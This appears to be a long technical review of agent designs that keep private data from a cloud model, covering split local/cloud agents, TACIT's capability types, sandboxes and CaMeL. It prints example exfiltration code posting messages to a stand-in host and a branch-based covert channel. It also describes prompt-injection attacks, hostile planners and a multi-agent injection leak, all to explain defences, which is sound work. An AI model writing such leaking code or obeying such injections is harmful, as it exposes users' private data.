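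The figures after the ± signs are standard errors. Radovič and colleagues ran each configuration once and estimated the errors by resampling the tasks 10,000 times. For the largest gain, treating the two scores as independent gives a standard error of √(3.9² + 3.8²), or about 5.4 points, so the gain is 2.7 times its error. None of the other five gains reaches twice its error. This method probably overstates the errors in the gains, because both agents attempted the same tasks and a task-by-task comparison would cancel some of the noise. But AppWorld's 750 tasks come from only 250 scenarios, so many are variants of one another, and resampling them as if they were unrelated probably understates the uncertainty. The benefit on normal tasks with a good cloud model looks real, but the size of the gains on challenge tasks is much less certain.

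Many AppWorld tasks need no interpretation, so the overall scores dilute the local model's effect. On the normal tasks where the cloud model chose to call `slm`, adding the local model raised the success rate from 0% to 28.6% with Qwen-coder, from 2.4% to 38.1% with Qwen-122B and from 13.8% to 48.3% with Qwen-27B. For Qwen-122B, there were 42 such tasks, of which code alone completed one and the split agent completed 16. These tasks account for 15 of the 17 extra tasks that the split agent completed with this model. The cloud models were evidently good at recognising where plain code would fail, although more than half of these tasks still failed with the local model's help.

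Some of the improvement may come from the instructions. They add about 3,700 tokens of advice to each program-writing prompt, and with Qwen-122B the split agent did 1.5 points better even on tasks where it never called the local model. A control agent with equally long instructions but no `slm` function would have separated the effect of the instructions from that of the local model. The extra text also makes the split agent cost more to run, since it sends the cloud model about 32% more input tokens than the code-only agent.

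### How small the local model can be

A nine-billion-parameter model is too large for many phones. To test whether a smaller one would be good enough, Radovič and colleagues gave smaller models the 1,584 questions that the 9B model had answered during the normal tasks. They could do this offline because each call is stateless, meaning its prompt contains everything the local model needs.

For simple outputs such as yes or no, a choice from a list, a number or a short text, a 2B model gave the same answer as the 9B model in 91.6% of calls. The 9B model matched its own earlier answers 97.0% of the time rather than 100%, because calculations vary slightly between graphics processors. Agreement doesn't prove that either model was right, and two models from the same family may make the same mistakes. In a separate check on the challenge tasks, a language model judged about 95% of the 9B model's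 answers correct.

The results were much worse when the cloud model did not follow its instructions and wrote calls for a structured list or object. Even the 9B model then matched its earlier answer only 69.9% of the time, which supports restricting calls to single values.

One wrong answer can change everything a program does afterwards, so the researchers also repeated the full experiment on the normal tasks with each size of local model.

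| Local model | Qwen-coder (%) | Qwen-122B (%) | Qwen-27B (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 33.3 | 42.3 | 45.8 |
| 0.8B | 33.9 | 48.8 | 52.4 |
| 2B | 36.9 | 51.2 | 61.3 |
| 9B | 38.7 | 52.4 | 60.7 |

The 2B local model did about as well as the 9B one, whichever of the three cloud models it was paired with. This is the best evidence for using the split on small devices. Models this small completed no tasks when they ran a reading loop alone, but the 2B model completed 61.3% when Qwen-27B wrote the programs. Its weights take about 2 GB at the eight-bit precision used in the experiment.

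*Three Roles, One Model* (McClendon, Gallego-Feliciano and colleagues, 2026) helps explain the difference. In that study, Qwen3-8B ran the whole loop on a single 24 GB graphics card and completed 5.4% of the normal tasks. It often lost track of important information, mishandled login credentials, called functions with the wrong arguments and repeated failed corrections. The score rose to 8.9% when the same model also summarised the history and reviewed its own code. In the split design, the program handles the credentials and keeps intermediate results in variables, so the local model has no long history to lose track of.

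### Why the reading loop still does better

A cloud model in a reading loop receives each result, so it can try another folder if the first was wrong. In the AppWorld experiment, it had up to 50 steps to do this. The code-writing agents were allowed five programs, and the cloud model received information about the data only when a program crashed.

"Not found" errors are especially hard to fix when the cloud model can't see the private data. If the program searches Kristin's texts for an amount that she gave by email, the cloud model receives an error with a label such as "wrong context" or "ambiguous question", but it can't look at the texts to see what went wrong. Radovič and colleagues found that after 55.6% of 448 "not found" failures, the next program failed with the same type of error. The next highest repeat rate was 35.6%, for requests that an app's API rejected as invalid. Each repeated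 failure uses up one of the five attempts and lengthens the prompt while giving the cloud model little new information.

They suggest having the local model inspect the program's variables after a crash and explain the problem to the cloud model. The local model would have to explain why the call failed without revealing the private content behind the failure, which is difficult. Alternatively, they propose that the local model attempt the repair on the device and involve the cloud model only if that fails.

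Repeated attempts can also have side effects. If a program pays Kristin and then crashes while sending the text, the next program may pay her again. To measure the effect on scores, Radovič and colleagues took the final program from each affected task and ran it again in a fresh copy of AppWorld. Leftover changes from earlier attempts accounted for at most 1.8 points in any configuration and less than half a point on average. They explain little of the gap, but a real user can't undo a duplicate payment by resetting her bank account.

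The retry loop also doesn't catch errors that don't stop the program. If `slm` returns 60 instead of 34.50, the program pays the wrong amount and finishes normally, so the device doesn't request another version. Such failures were common in earlier AppWorld agents. *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* (2026) examined failed runs from two agent designs that report whether they have succeeded, one of which writes complete programs. The agents reported success in 1,425 of these runs and failure in only 454. The models were older ones such as GPT-4o, so the proportion may be lower now, but a program that checks only for crashes would still miss such errors.

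### Running the whole loop locally

The study also compared the split agent with a fully local reading loop, using the same 9B model on the device. The split agent completed 52.4% of the normal tasks when Qwen-122B wrote the programs, while the loop completed 45.2%. The split agent's local model also processed between ten and a hundred times fewer input tokens and generated 1.8 times fewer output tokens. The tenfold figure applies if the loop can reuse its earlier processing at every step. The longest prompt in a typical task was about 3,700 tokens for the split agent and 12,000 for the loop, so the split agent needs less working memory. Radovič and colleagues expect these reductions to save time and battery power, but they measured neither.

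The advantage depends on a capable cloud model. With Qwen-coder writing the programs, the split agent reached only 38.7%, so a user with a 9B model would have done better running the whole loop locally.

The case for the split is even weaker on a machine with somewhat more memory. The 12-billion-parameter Gemma model scored 73% in a reading loop, higher than any split agent in the study, assuming that its score is for the normal tasks. Its weights take 6 GB at four bits, but the researchers tested it at eight bits, which takes about twice the space. McClendon and colleagues found that Qwen3-8B scored lower at four bits, even with room for a longer history.

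Each model in this experiment, including the "cloud" one, ran on a single graphics processor, and Qwen-27B's weights need roughly 27 GB at eight bits. An organisation that owned such a processor could let Qwen-27B read the data directly and complete 81.0% of the normal tasks without sending any data outside. The split therefore makes most sense for a phone or an ordinary laptop, or when the user wants programs from a closed model that only its provider can run.

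Training is making local loops more competitive. In *Entropy-Preserving Reinforcement Learning*, Petrenko, Lipkin and colleagues (2026) trained open Qwen models on AppWorld and reported success rates of 79% on normal tasks and 71% on challenge tasks. The challenge result is 12 points above that of the reading loop with untrained Qwen-27B. Smaller models still score lower after training. In *Terrarium* (2026), training raised Qwen3-4B's score from 16.7% to 30.4% on normal tasks and from 9.6% to 21.1% on challenge tasks. Xu and colleagues also improved a 4B model by training eight copies in parallel, which took about 2,100 GPU-hours. Users could download a trained model without paying for the training, but a model trained on AppWorld's apps may not do as well with other software.

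Scores from different studies are hard to compare closely. Even before training, *Terrarium*'s 4B model did almost three times as well on the normal tasks as any model of that size in the experiments by Radovič and colleagues, but the two studies used different models and different software around them. The way attempts are counted also matters. Qwen3-8B scored 5.4% in a single attempt by McClendon and colleagues, who cite another team's average of 15% over four attempts for the same model.

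No other team appears to have published a replication of the split experiment. In the closest study, *When Cloud Agents Meet Device Agents*, Rainone, Belli and colleagues (2026) examined several ways of combining cloud and device models and found that the best arrangement depends heavily on the task and on what the designer wants to optimise.

A test with a frontier model in the cloud role would be especially useful because users would have the most reason to keep private data from such a model. On normal tasks, the models that wrote better programs without help also gained more from `slm`. Qwen-coder gained 5.4 points, Qwen-122B gained 10.1 and Qwen-27B gained 14.9. A frontier model might gain even more, but three models are too few to establish a trend, and Qwen-27B still scored more than 20 points below its own reading loop.

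## Checking the program with types before it runs

In the grocery task, the cloud model never receives Kristin's messages, but its program holds all of them in an ordinary variable. One extra line would be enough to send them somewhere else:

```python
messages = get_texts(kristin)
http_post("https://collect.example", messages)
```

A hostile cloud model could write that line on purpose. An honest one could do similar damage by accident, for example by saving the messages to a shared folder or leaving in a `print` statement whose output goes back to the cloud model. Few users can read code well enough to spot such lines, and reviewing a program for every request would be tedious.

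Limiting which files and websites the program can reach solves only part of the problem. An agent that works on private contracts may need both to read them and to contact its provider. Odersky and colleagues point out that the agent can then leak data through two permitted steps, reading a file and sending data from it in a message.

Their system, TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), checks for such flows before the program runs. The cloud model has to write in Scala, whose compiler can work out which files, connections and output channels each piece of code can use. If the compiler can't establish that the private data won't leak, it rejects the whole program and sends the cloud model an error message. The compiler works from the code alone, so this message can't include text from an email or a bank statement, as the error trace from a crashed program can.

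### What the user has to trust

Everything is untrusted except the compiler, the runtime, the optional local model and the library that programs use to access files and networks. The untrusted parts include the software that drives the agent and any text from web pages, tools or protected files.

Hidden instructions in a web page may influence the cloud model. TACIT doesn't try to prevent this, but it checks the resulting program like any other, so a manipulated model can do no more than a hostile one.

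Existing agents such as Claude Code can use TACIT without modification, because it connects to them through MCP. But these agents also have their own tools for reading files and running commands, and the compiler doesn't check what the agents do with them. The project's documentation on GitHub, lampepfl's *TACIT*, advises users to switch the built-in tools off. If they are left on, the agent can bypass all the protection described below.

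### Recording capabilities in types

A TACIT program can't open a file just by naming it. It needs a capability, an unforgeable value that grants a particular power, and it gets one by asking the library:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/home/ana/project") {
  val notes = access("notes.txt")
  notes.write("Call the bank")
}
```

The library grants access only to that folder, and only until the block of code in braces ends. Similar functions let a program run listed commands or contact listed hosts. The library, rather than the compiler, checks the paths, commands and hosts, and it does so while the program runs.

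The compiler's part is to keep track of where each capability goes. A type normally describes what kind of value something is, such as text or a whole number. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds the set of capabilities that the value can reach. For example, a function that writes a piece of text to a file `f` has the type

`String ->{f} Unit`

It takes text (`String`), returns nothing useful (`Unit`) and may use `f`. A function that capitalizes text has the type `String -> String`, with no capabilities listed. Programmers call such a function pure because it calculates a result and has no other effect. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* describes a function with the thin arrow `->` as capturing nothing, and one with the fat arrow `=>` as a function that may capture anything.

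The compiler infers most of these sets. If the body of a function uses `f`, or calls another function that does, the compiler adds `f` to the set. The set may include capabilities that the function never uses when it runs, so the compiler can reject a harmless program.

The sets also prevent a program from keeping access after a block ends. In one test, an agent wrote code that returned a list of file handles from a `requestFileSystem` block. Each handle carried the folder's capability in its type, so the compiler rejected the code.

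### Wrapped values

To protect private data, the user marks some folders as classified. When a program reads a file from one of them, the library returns the contents as a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. The program can compute on this wrapped value but can't unwrap it. The full design includes a method for unwrapping it, but that method requires a permission the agent doesn't have.

Programs compute on the contents with a method called `map`:

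```scala
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` is the type of the hidden content and `U` is the type of the result. The method applies the function `op` to the content and wraps the result. The thin arrow means that `op` must be pure, which protects the content.

```scala
val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")

// Accepted: the function only calculates
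val tidy = key.map { k => k.trim }

// Rejected: the function prints
key.map { k => println(k) }
```

Removing the spaces around a key needs no capability, but printing does, because TACIT's `println` requires a capability for output. The compiler therefore includes that capability in the capability set of the second function, which prints. `map` only accepts functions whose capability set is empty, so the compiler rejects the program.

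Less direct methods fail for the same reason. A program can't write the key to a file inside `map`, and it can't request access to a new folder there, because `requestFileSystem` needs the output capability too. It also can't copy the key into a variable outside the function and print it afterwards:

```scala
var copy = ""
key.map { k => copy = k }
println(copy)
```

Changing a variable outside the function counts as an effect, so the compiler rejects the second line.

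Odersky and colleagues identify three properties that the language needs for this to work. Capability safety means that a program can't forge a capability or hide that it is using one. Capability completeness means that every action that affects security requires a capability, unless the runtime contains the action some other way. If a single function could open a network connection without a capability, a program could call it inside `map` and the compiler would accept it. Local purity is the ability to require that one piece of code has no effects while the rest of the program can still read files and contact websites.

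### Comparing contracts without reading them

Odersky and colleagues illustrate the design with a user who asks an agent to compare a set of contracts and summarise the changes. The contracts' contents must not reach the cloud model or redirect the agent.

The program gets access to a document database and an output file. It also gets a function that finds the differences between two texts, and one called `chat` that sends text to the local model. In simplified form, the central part could look like this:

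```scala
val pair = oldContract.aggregate(newContract)
val changes = pair.map { (a, b) => diff(a, b) }
val summary = chat("Summarise these changes:", changes)
writeClassified("contracts/summary.txt", summary)
```

The database returns each contract wrapped in its own container. `map` can open only one container at a time, so the `aggregate` method combines the two. The comparison is a pure calculation, so the compiler accepts it, and the list of changes comes out wrapped. The program then passes this list to the local model and saves the reply in a protected file.

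The `chat` function has this type:

```scala
def chat(prompt: String, message: Classified[String]): Classified[String]
```

The cloud model writes the prompt as ordinary text. The local model reads the contents of the message, and its reply goes straight back into a wrapper. The wrapper is the main difference from Radovič and colleagues' `slm` function, which gives the program an ordinary number or piece of text.

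The `chat` function needs no capability, so the compiler treats a call to the local model as a pure calculation. This is correct only if the model has no tools and retains nothing between calls, which the compiler can't check. It also can't check where the model runs. TACIT accepts the address of any server with an OpenAI-compatible interface, so if the user enters a cloud provider's address, the contracts will go to that provider.

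As in the Dual LLM pattern, an instruction hidden in a contract can still corrupt the summary, for example by making the local model leave out a new penalty clause.

### A session over two turns

With TACIT, the cloud model can work in a loop, submitting a short program, reading the printed output and then writing the next program. It can read ordinary files, such as public source code, in the usual way.

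TACIT sends a program's output to two channels. The normal channel feeds into the cloud model's context, while the secure channel goes only to the user's terminal. When a program prints an ordinary value, the same text appears on both. When it prints a wrapped value, the secure channel shows the content and the normal channel shows "Classified(****)".

Odersky and colleagues give this example of a session, in which the program keeps its variables from one turn to the next:

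```scala
// First turn: the user asks for a summary of a contract
val summary = requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val doc = readClassified("secret/contract.txt")
  chat("Summarize:", doc)
}
println(summary)

// Second turn: the user asks a follow-up question
val length = summary.map(_.length)
println(length)
```

| Printed value | What the user sees | What the cloud model sees |
|---|---|---|
| `summary` | The text of the summary | Classified(****) |
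| `length` | The number of characters | Classified(****) |

By the second turn, the program's access to the `/data` folder has expired. The summary is still available because it is a value and grants no access, but it remains wrapped. Its length is also wrapped because the program calculated it from protected text.

The cloud model can write the second program without reading the summary, since the program only requires that `summary` contain text. But if the user asks whether the third change is serious, the cloud model has no description of that change and has to forward the question to the local model. And if the user quotes a sentence from the summary in the next request, the quotation goes to the cloud model like anything else the user types.

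Computer scientists call the ideal behind this design noninterference. Let *q* be everything the user types, *P* the ordinary data, and *d* and *d*′ any two possible versions of the wrapped data. A system has noninterference if the cloud view *V* is the same for both versions, given the same random choices by the models:

*V*(*q*, *P*, *d*) = *V*(*q*, *P*, *d*′).

Nobody can then use the cloud view to tell one version from the other. In terms of the earlier measure of leakage, if *D* is the wrapped data,

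*I*(*D*; *V* | *q*, *P*) = 0.

TACIT doesn't achieve this completely, because the cloud model may learn something from how long a program takes or whether it finishes.

The equation also doesn't protect data that the user never marked as classified, which belongs to *P*. Glama's *TACIT*, an MCP server directory's copy of a later version of the documentation, lists the locations that TACIT protects by default, including `.ssh` and `.env`, where developers keep keys and passwords. A divorce settlement in a Documents folder would reach the cloud model as ordinary text unless the user had marked the folder. The published library also gives a file's name and size as ordinary values, and Odersky and colleagues mention no exception for classified files. In the example, the cloud model may be able to learn the contract's size even though the summary's length is hidden.

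### Acting on a wrapped answer

Summaries suit this design because only the user needs to read them. The grocery task is harder. If the local model returns the amount owed to Kristin as a `Classified[Double]`, the program can't pass it to a payment function that expects an ordinary number. It also can't check whether the amount is over $50 and then ask the user for approval, because the check would have to happen inside `map`, where the program isn't allowed to ask the user anything.

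The trusted library therefore needs a payment function that accepts a wrapped amount. This function declassifies the amount by deliberately revealing it to the payment service. Leaving that choice to the library's maintainer is safer than leaving it to the cloud model, but it means that each new kind of action on private data needs new trusted code.

The later version of TACIT includes functions of this kind for web requests. A program can log in to a service by sending a wrapped password or key to a host on the user's list, without exposing it to the cloud model. It can also send a wrapped document and receive a wrapped reply. This makes the agent more useful, but the user has to trust every listed host with any protected file, because the untrusted program chooses what to send. If the list included a website where anyone can publish text, a hostile program could post the user's documents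 there for the cloud model's operator to collect.

TACIT's developers also warn that wrapping protects confidentiality but not integrity. A program can wrap its own text and write it over a classified file. For example, a program could give an attacker access to the user's computer by replacing the file that lists which keys may log in. Users can prevent this by making classified files read-only, but TACIT allows writing by default.

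### Closing the ways around the types

Scala normally lets programmers override the type system. For example, a type cast tells the compiler to treat a value as if it had a different type, so a program could use one to make the compiler accept a printing function as pure. TACIT therefore requires programs to stay within Scala's *Safe Mode*, a restricted part of the language. Safe Mode forbids unchecked casts, annotations that turn checks off, and reflection, which lets a program find and call code by name while running.

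Restrictions on the program would achieve little if it could call a library function that bypassed them. In safe mode, a program can use a global library object only if the object also compiles in safe mode or a programmer has marked it `@assumeSafe`, which the compiler doesn't verify. The documentation gives the example of a function that asks the user to confirm each email before passing it to an ordinary mail library. Marking that function as safe is reasonable if users read what they are approving, but Willison doubted that they would.

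A mistaken `@assumeSafe` can break the design's privacy protection. Suppose a company marks a text-cleaning function as safe without noticing that it reports errors to an outside logging service. The compiler would then let programs call the function on wrapped data, and fragments of private documents could end up in the log.

Safe mode also permits exceptions, which a program raises when something goes wrong, although their messages can carry private text. Tracking every possible exception in types would be impractical because so many operations can fail, from dividing by zero to running out of memory. Instead, the runtime catches exceptions and turns them into values, which the library can wrap.

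The paper on TACIT describes the compiler as enforcing safe mode. According to the earlier documentation, however, TACIT searched each program's text for forbidden patterns, and the developers planned to move to the compiler's own safe mode later. The later version still runs the pattern search and can also turn on the compiler's safe mode. A pattern search is weaker than a type check because it catches only the tricks its developers thought of. The compiler has always handled capture checking, which makes `map` reject functions that print.

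### The safety benchmark

To test the protection, Odersky and colleagues set up a software project with a secret folder of API keys, a database and classified documents. They wrote 12 legitimate tasks. Some, such as listing the functions described in a README, involved only public files. Others, such as summarising a classified incident report or removing names from employee reviews, required private content.

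They combined each task with ten prompt injections, for 120 trials per model. The simplest injections were instructions in developers' notes or code comments. More elaborate ones imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were only test data, faked errors that could be "fixed" with a password, or supplied ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. In 11 further trials, the user's own request was malicious. Five requests asked directly for secrets, and six used a pretext, such as an administrator needing to replace passwords in an emergency.

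Each model attempted every trial twice, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secure with wrapping (%) | Secure without wrapping (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100 | 100 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100 | 81.8 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100 | 98.5 |
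| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100 | 97.5 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100 | 27.3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100 | 91.6 |

Neither model's output contained a secret when the secrets were wrapped. Without wrapping, there were 13 leaks in 262 trials. Ten came from the 22 malicious requests, and the other three came from injections against MiniMax. Sonnet leaked nothing under injection even without wrapping, so its 120 injection trials can't show whether wrapping makes a difference. The evidence for wrapping therefore comes mostly from the malicious requests, and with only 11 of them per model, a single leak changes a model's score by nine points.

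The scoring would also have missed a program that uploaded a secret or saved it in an unprotected folder without printing it. The compiler should reject such programs, and Odersky and colleagues give examples of agents' code that it did reject, but the 100% scores don't measure how reliably it does so. The scores also don't mean that TACIT would stop a dishonest user from obtaining the keys, since the secure channel shows wrapped values to whoever is using the terminal.

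A larger gap is that the attacks tried to persuade a model to reveal secrets, while TACIT's threat model includes a cloud model that deliberately tries to reveal them. Such a model would look for a bug in the compiler or a badly designed library function. Agents that could break into Hugging Face might be good at this, but no model in the trials was instructed to try. The 100% scores are good evidence that TACIT works as designed against ordinary manipulation, but a serious test of the guarantee would require paying skilled attackers, human or AI, to find a program that compiles but leaks private data.

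Wrapping did not make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the 120 legitimate trials with wrapping and 83.3% without, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's low score without wrapping is partly an artefact of the setup, because Sonnet often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task. The scores show that agents can handle some private documents through a local model, although they come from only 12 different tasks.

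### What the typed programs cost

Cloud models might write Scala with capture checking badly, because they have seen much less of it than Python. Odersky and colleagues tested this on τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations for an airline and a shop. They compared agents that made ordinary tool calls with agents that wrote Scala programs, and averaged the results over ten runs.

| Model | Airline, tool calls (%) | Airline, Scala (%) | Retail, tool calls (%) | Retail, Scala (%) |
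|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

Scala scored higher in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 points. On SWE-bench Lite, however, which contains 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five problems. Odersky and colleagues suggest this may be because coding agents rely on shell commands, which are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

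They attribute the gains on τ²-bench to clearer data formats and helpful error messages from the compiler. The gains may also come from combining several steps in one program, which would help in Python too. The study had no Python agent for comparison, so it can't separate the effect of types from the effect of writing code.

The τ²-bench results show that models can write this kind of Scala, but the agents worked with ordinary customer records that the cloud model could print and read. The results therefore don't measure how much performance an agent loses when its cloud model can't see the data. The AppWorld experiment is a better guide to that loss.

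Compilation errors were rare on τ²-bench. DeepSeek had to correct 7.93% of its airline programs, and no other combination of model and domain exceeded 1.6%. When a program did fail to compile, the model usually fixed it in one or two attempts. Some common errors were unrelated to security, such as failing to handle a value that might be missing or mistyping a dollar sign.

The rate depends on the task. In a later system from the same group, the model writes a piece of code whenever a running program reaches a gap. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) reports that the compiler rejected 8.6% of these pieces on BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of difficult research questions, with an average of 0.7 retries per question.

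These rejections are better than crashes because they happen before any of the program has run. Zhao and colleagues demonstrate this with code that subtracts 50 from an account balance and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler finds the error in the last line, so the balance stays at 100. A Python agent could have made the deduction before it crashed, so a user might end up paying Kristin twice. But types can't prevent every crash. If a website stops responding halfway through a program, the earlier steps have already taken effect.

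Checking a program takes little time compared with the cloud model writing it. TACIT compiles a typical program in under a second once the compiler has warmed up. *What's in the Box* (2025) found that capture checking took less than 15% of total compilation time in tests on Scala's standard library.

### What the proofs cover

A type system is sound if every program it accepts behaves as its types promise. Researchers have proved this for the basic rules of capture checking, and a computer has verified the proofs. The proofs are much stronger evidence than a benchmark result, because they cover every program that follows the rules, including any an attacker might write.

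The proofs don't cover everything in TACIT. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that a further argument would be needed to show that safe mode delivers capability safety and local purity. The proofs are about core calculi, small mathematical models of a language. Scala has many more features, and its compiler may contain mistakes that the models don't.

Later work has extended the theory without closing this gap. *System Capybara* (2026) proves memory safety and other properties for a core calculus, but it doesn't prove that translating the fuller language into that core preserves a program's meaning. In *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026) found that Scala's types couldn't express some restrictions that its standard library needs, and said this had kept parts of the library outside capture checking. One of their examples is `Try`, the class that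 TACIT uses to catch exceptions. They extended the type system to handle such cases.

Any of the trusted components could also contain an ordinary bug. TACIT's users have to trust an entire compiler and language runtime, which contain far more code than the part of OpenSSH that kept its privileges. Odersky and colleagues recommend running TACIT inside a sandbox, so that an attacker who escapes from the language would still have to get out of the sandbox.

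### Adopting the approach

An organisation using TACIT has to describe its own tools in Scala. The reusable part, including the wrapper and the connection to the local model, is about 1,000 lines. The descriptions of the airline and retail tools took a few hundred lines each, similar in length to the JSON descriptions they replaced. Agents can help write these descriptions, but people need to review them, and changes to the reusable part require someone who understands capture checking. The software also depends on nightly builds of Scala, which can change from one day to the next.

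Odersky and colleagues exclude some problems from their aims. TACIT doesn't check whether a program does what the user asked, so a program that summarises the wrong contract can pass every check. If a program may run an outside command, the compiler also can't control what that command does with the files it can reach, so protection depends on which commands are permitted.

The method doesn't depend on Scala. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes ELBA, a similar system built in Haskell, where every function's type already shows whether it can have effects. If an agent's task is to return a whole number, ELBA rejects any program that also tries to delete files, because deleting files would change the program's type. Haskell has loopholes too, which ELBA closes with Safe Haskell, a restricted version of the language that is much older than Scala's safe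 mode.

Zhou and colleagues write the whole application in Haskell, including the code that calls the model and handles retries. The agent then has no built-in tools that the compiler doesn't check, so users don't have to remember to switch them off. But existing agents can't simply connect to ELBA as they can to TACIT, so someone has to rewrite the application around it.

In either language, the user or organisation must still decide what to protect. VirtusLab, a software company that works with Scala, warns against classifying too much, because agents' usefulness comes largely from reading and understanding files and emails. A local model can make up for only part of the usefulness lost by classifying data.

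## Controlling the program while it runs

A compiler can reject a program that would print Kristin's messages, but it can't tell whether the address in a variable is Kristin's or a stranger's, because the variable has no value until the program runs. TACIT's checks also don't help an agent whose cloud model writes ordinary Python, as in the AppWorld experiment. Sandboxes, taint tracking and approval of individual actions work while the program runs, when the values exist.

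### What a sandbox restricts

A sandbox limits which files a program can open, which network hosts it can contact and which system calls it can make. System calls are requests to the operating system, such as to open a file or start another program. An operating-system sandbox enforces its limits whatever language the program is written in, and applies them to any outside command the program starts. Odersky and colleagues note that two coding agents, Claude Code and OpenCode, already run generated code in a sandbox.

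These limits apply to each operation separately, so an agent allowed to read a private contract and contact the cloud model can still send the contract to that model. The sandbox doesn't record where the text in a message came from. Similarly, Tallam and Miller (2025) point out in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that if a sandbox permits outgoing email, a manipulated agent can still put sensitive data in a plausible message.

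### Removing the network connection

The split design allows a much stricter sandbox because the program never needs to contact the cloud model. The user's software can run the program in a process with no network interface and pass its queries to the local model through a pipe, a direct channel between two processes on the same machine. The software can also make the private files read-only, provide an empty scratch folder and show the program's output only to the user. The line that posts Kristin's messages to `collect.example` then fails, whichever networking library it uses. A stray `print` shows the messages only to the user, who already has them.

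For a task such as adding up a year of bank transactions, this gives nearly complete protection, as long as crash reports also stay on the device. The program can calculate anything but cannot send the result off the device. The user doesn't need a special programming language or labels on the data.

Private data can still leak in a few indirect ways. If the scratch folder is inside a folder that syncs to online storage, the syncing software will upload whatever the program saves there. A later task might read a leftover file and pass it to the cloud model as ordinary text, so the user's software should delete the scratch folder after each task. If the display loads images from the web, a program can put the user's bank balance in an image's address, and the display will send the balance to the image's host.

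Many tasks require the agent to act on the outside world, though. To repay Kristin, the program has to reach a payment service. The user's software can use a broker, a small trusted program outside the sandbox that holds the login details and carries out a short list of operations on request, much as OpenSSH's monitor does. The sandboxed program sends a payment request to the broker and never accesses the network itself.

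The broker still has to accept values from an untrusted program. A hostile program could request a one-cent payment to an accomplice, with Kristin's messages in the payment note. Payments are on the broker's list and one cent is below any sensible limit, so the broker can't detect the leak unless it has a record of where the note's text came from.

### Following the data with CaMeL

Taint tracking provides this information by labelling each value with its origin. CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) applies taint tracking to agents. CaMeL builds on the Dual LLM pattern, but its privileged model writes a complete program instead of issuing one command at a time. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes how CaMeL works.

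The privileged model receives the user's request and descriptions of the available tools, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A custom interpreter runs the program and uses labels to track where each value came from and which other values it depends on. When the program needs to extract something from untrusted text, such as a date from an email, it calls the quarantined model, which has no tools. Before every tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments' labels against a security policy. A policy might forbid `send_email` if the text derives from private data and the recipient isn't allowed to read that data.

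A simplified version of the labels shows how such a policy works. Let *S*(*x*) be the set of sources that a value *x* came from and *R*(*x*) the set of people who may read it. If the program computes *z* from *x* and *y*, the interpreter sets

*S*(*z*) = *S*(*x*) ∪ *S*(*y*) and *R*(*z*) = *R*(*x*) ∩ *R*(*y*).

When the program computes a new value *z* from two inputs, *z* has all the sources of both, and only people who may read both inputs may read it. If *R*(*z*) is the set of people who may read *z*, the email policy allows the program to send *z* to a person *p* only if *p* ∈ *R*(*z*).

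Suppose a user asks the agent to send Kristin a plan for their trip, based on their text messages and the user's notes. Kristin may read the messages, but only the user may read the notes. The local model writes the plan from both, so the interpreter labels the plan as readable only by the user and blocks the email, even if the plan contains nothing from the notes. Kim, Choi and Lee (2025) explain in *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* why a more precise label is hard to justify. Any part of a language model's input can influence its output to some extent, and measuring how much usually requires access to the model's internals. The safe choice is to give the output the combined restrictions of all the inputs, although this blocks some harmless messages.

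The program can avoid some of this by making narrower calls. If it gives the local model only the text messages when extracting the travel dates, Kristin can still read the dates.

### When the planner is hostile

CaMeL is designed to stop prompt injection, so it assumes that the attacker controls only the data. As Tallam and Miller point out, it treats the user's prompt as trusted. It also relies on the privileged model to write an honest program. Its main guarantee is control-flow integrity, which means that text the agent reads can't add steps to the program. This doesn't protect a user whose cloud model wrote a harmful step into the original program. In the split design, that protection has to come from the policies and accurate labels.

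Accurate labels are harder to maintain when the program's author is trying to defeat them. In this constructed example, neither web address contains anything from the letter:

```python
if "divorce" in letter:
    fetch("https://shop.example/a")
else:
    fetch("https://shop.example/b")
```

The shop's operator can still tell from the request whether the letter mentions a divorce. Each request reveals one bit, so at eight bits per character a program could send a 1,000-character letter in 8,000 requests. Tallam and Miller give a similar example in which a program takes a secret number and contacts a server that many times, so anyone reading the server's log can learn the number.

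To catch these flows, the interpreter must apply the condition's label to everything that happens inside the branch or loop. Tallam and Miller recommend a strict mode that blocks state-changing tool calls in a loop whose length depends on a secret, or asks the user to confirm them. They also suggest capping the number of repetitions and combining repeated calls into one. These flows can be a side issue for CaMeL because an honest planner would rarely write code that causes them, but a hostile planner could do so deliberately.

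The quarantined model also has to run on the user's side, which CaMeL's designers didn't test, according to Radovič and colleagues. The interpreter has to run there too, because it holds the values.

### Labels that disappear in text

An interpreter can only track values that stay inside it. Odersky and colleagues note that a value loses its label once it enters a model's conversation as ordinary language.

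Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated the consequences with three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of some job applicants on Slack. The coordinator got the data from a database agent, then sent a notification agent a single piece of text containing both the instruction to send "this summary" and the summary itself. The researchers had hidden in the database an instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address. The coordinator and the database agent both treated this instruction as data. The notification agent received it as part of its user's request, and its privileged model wrote a program that sent the email.

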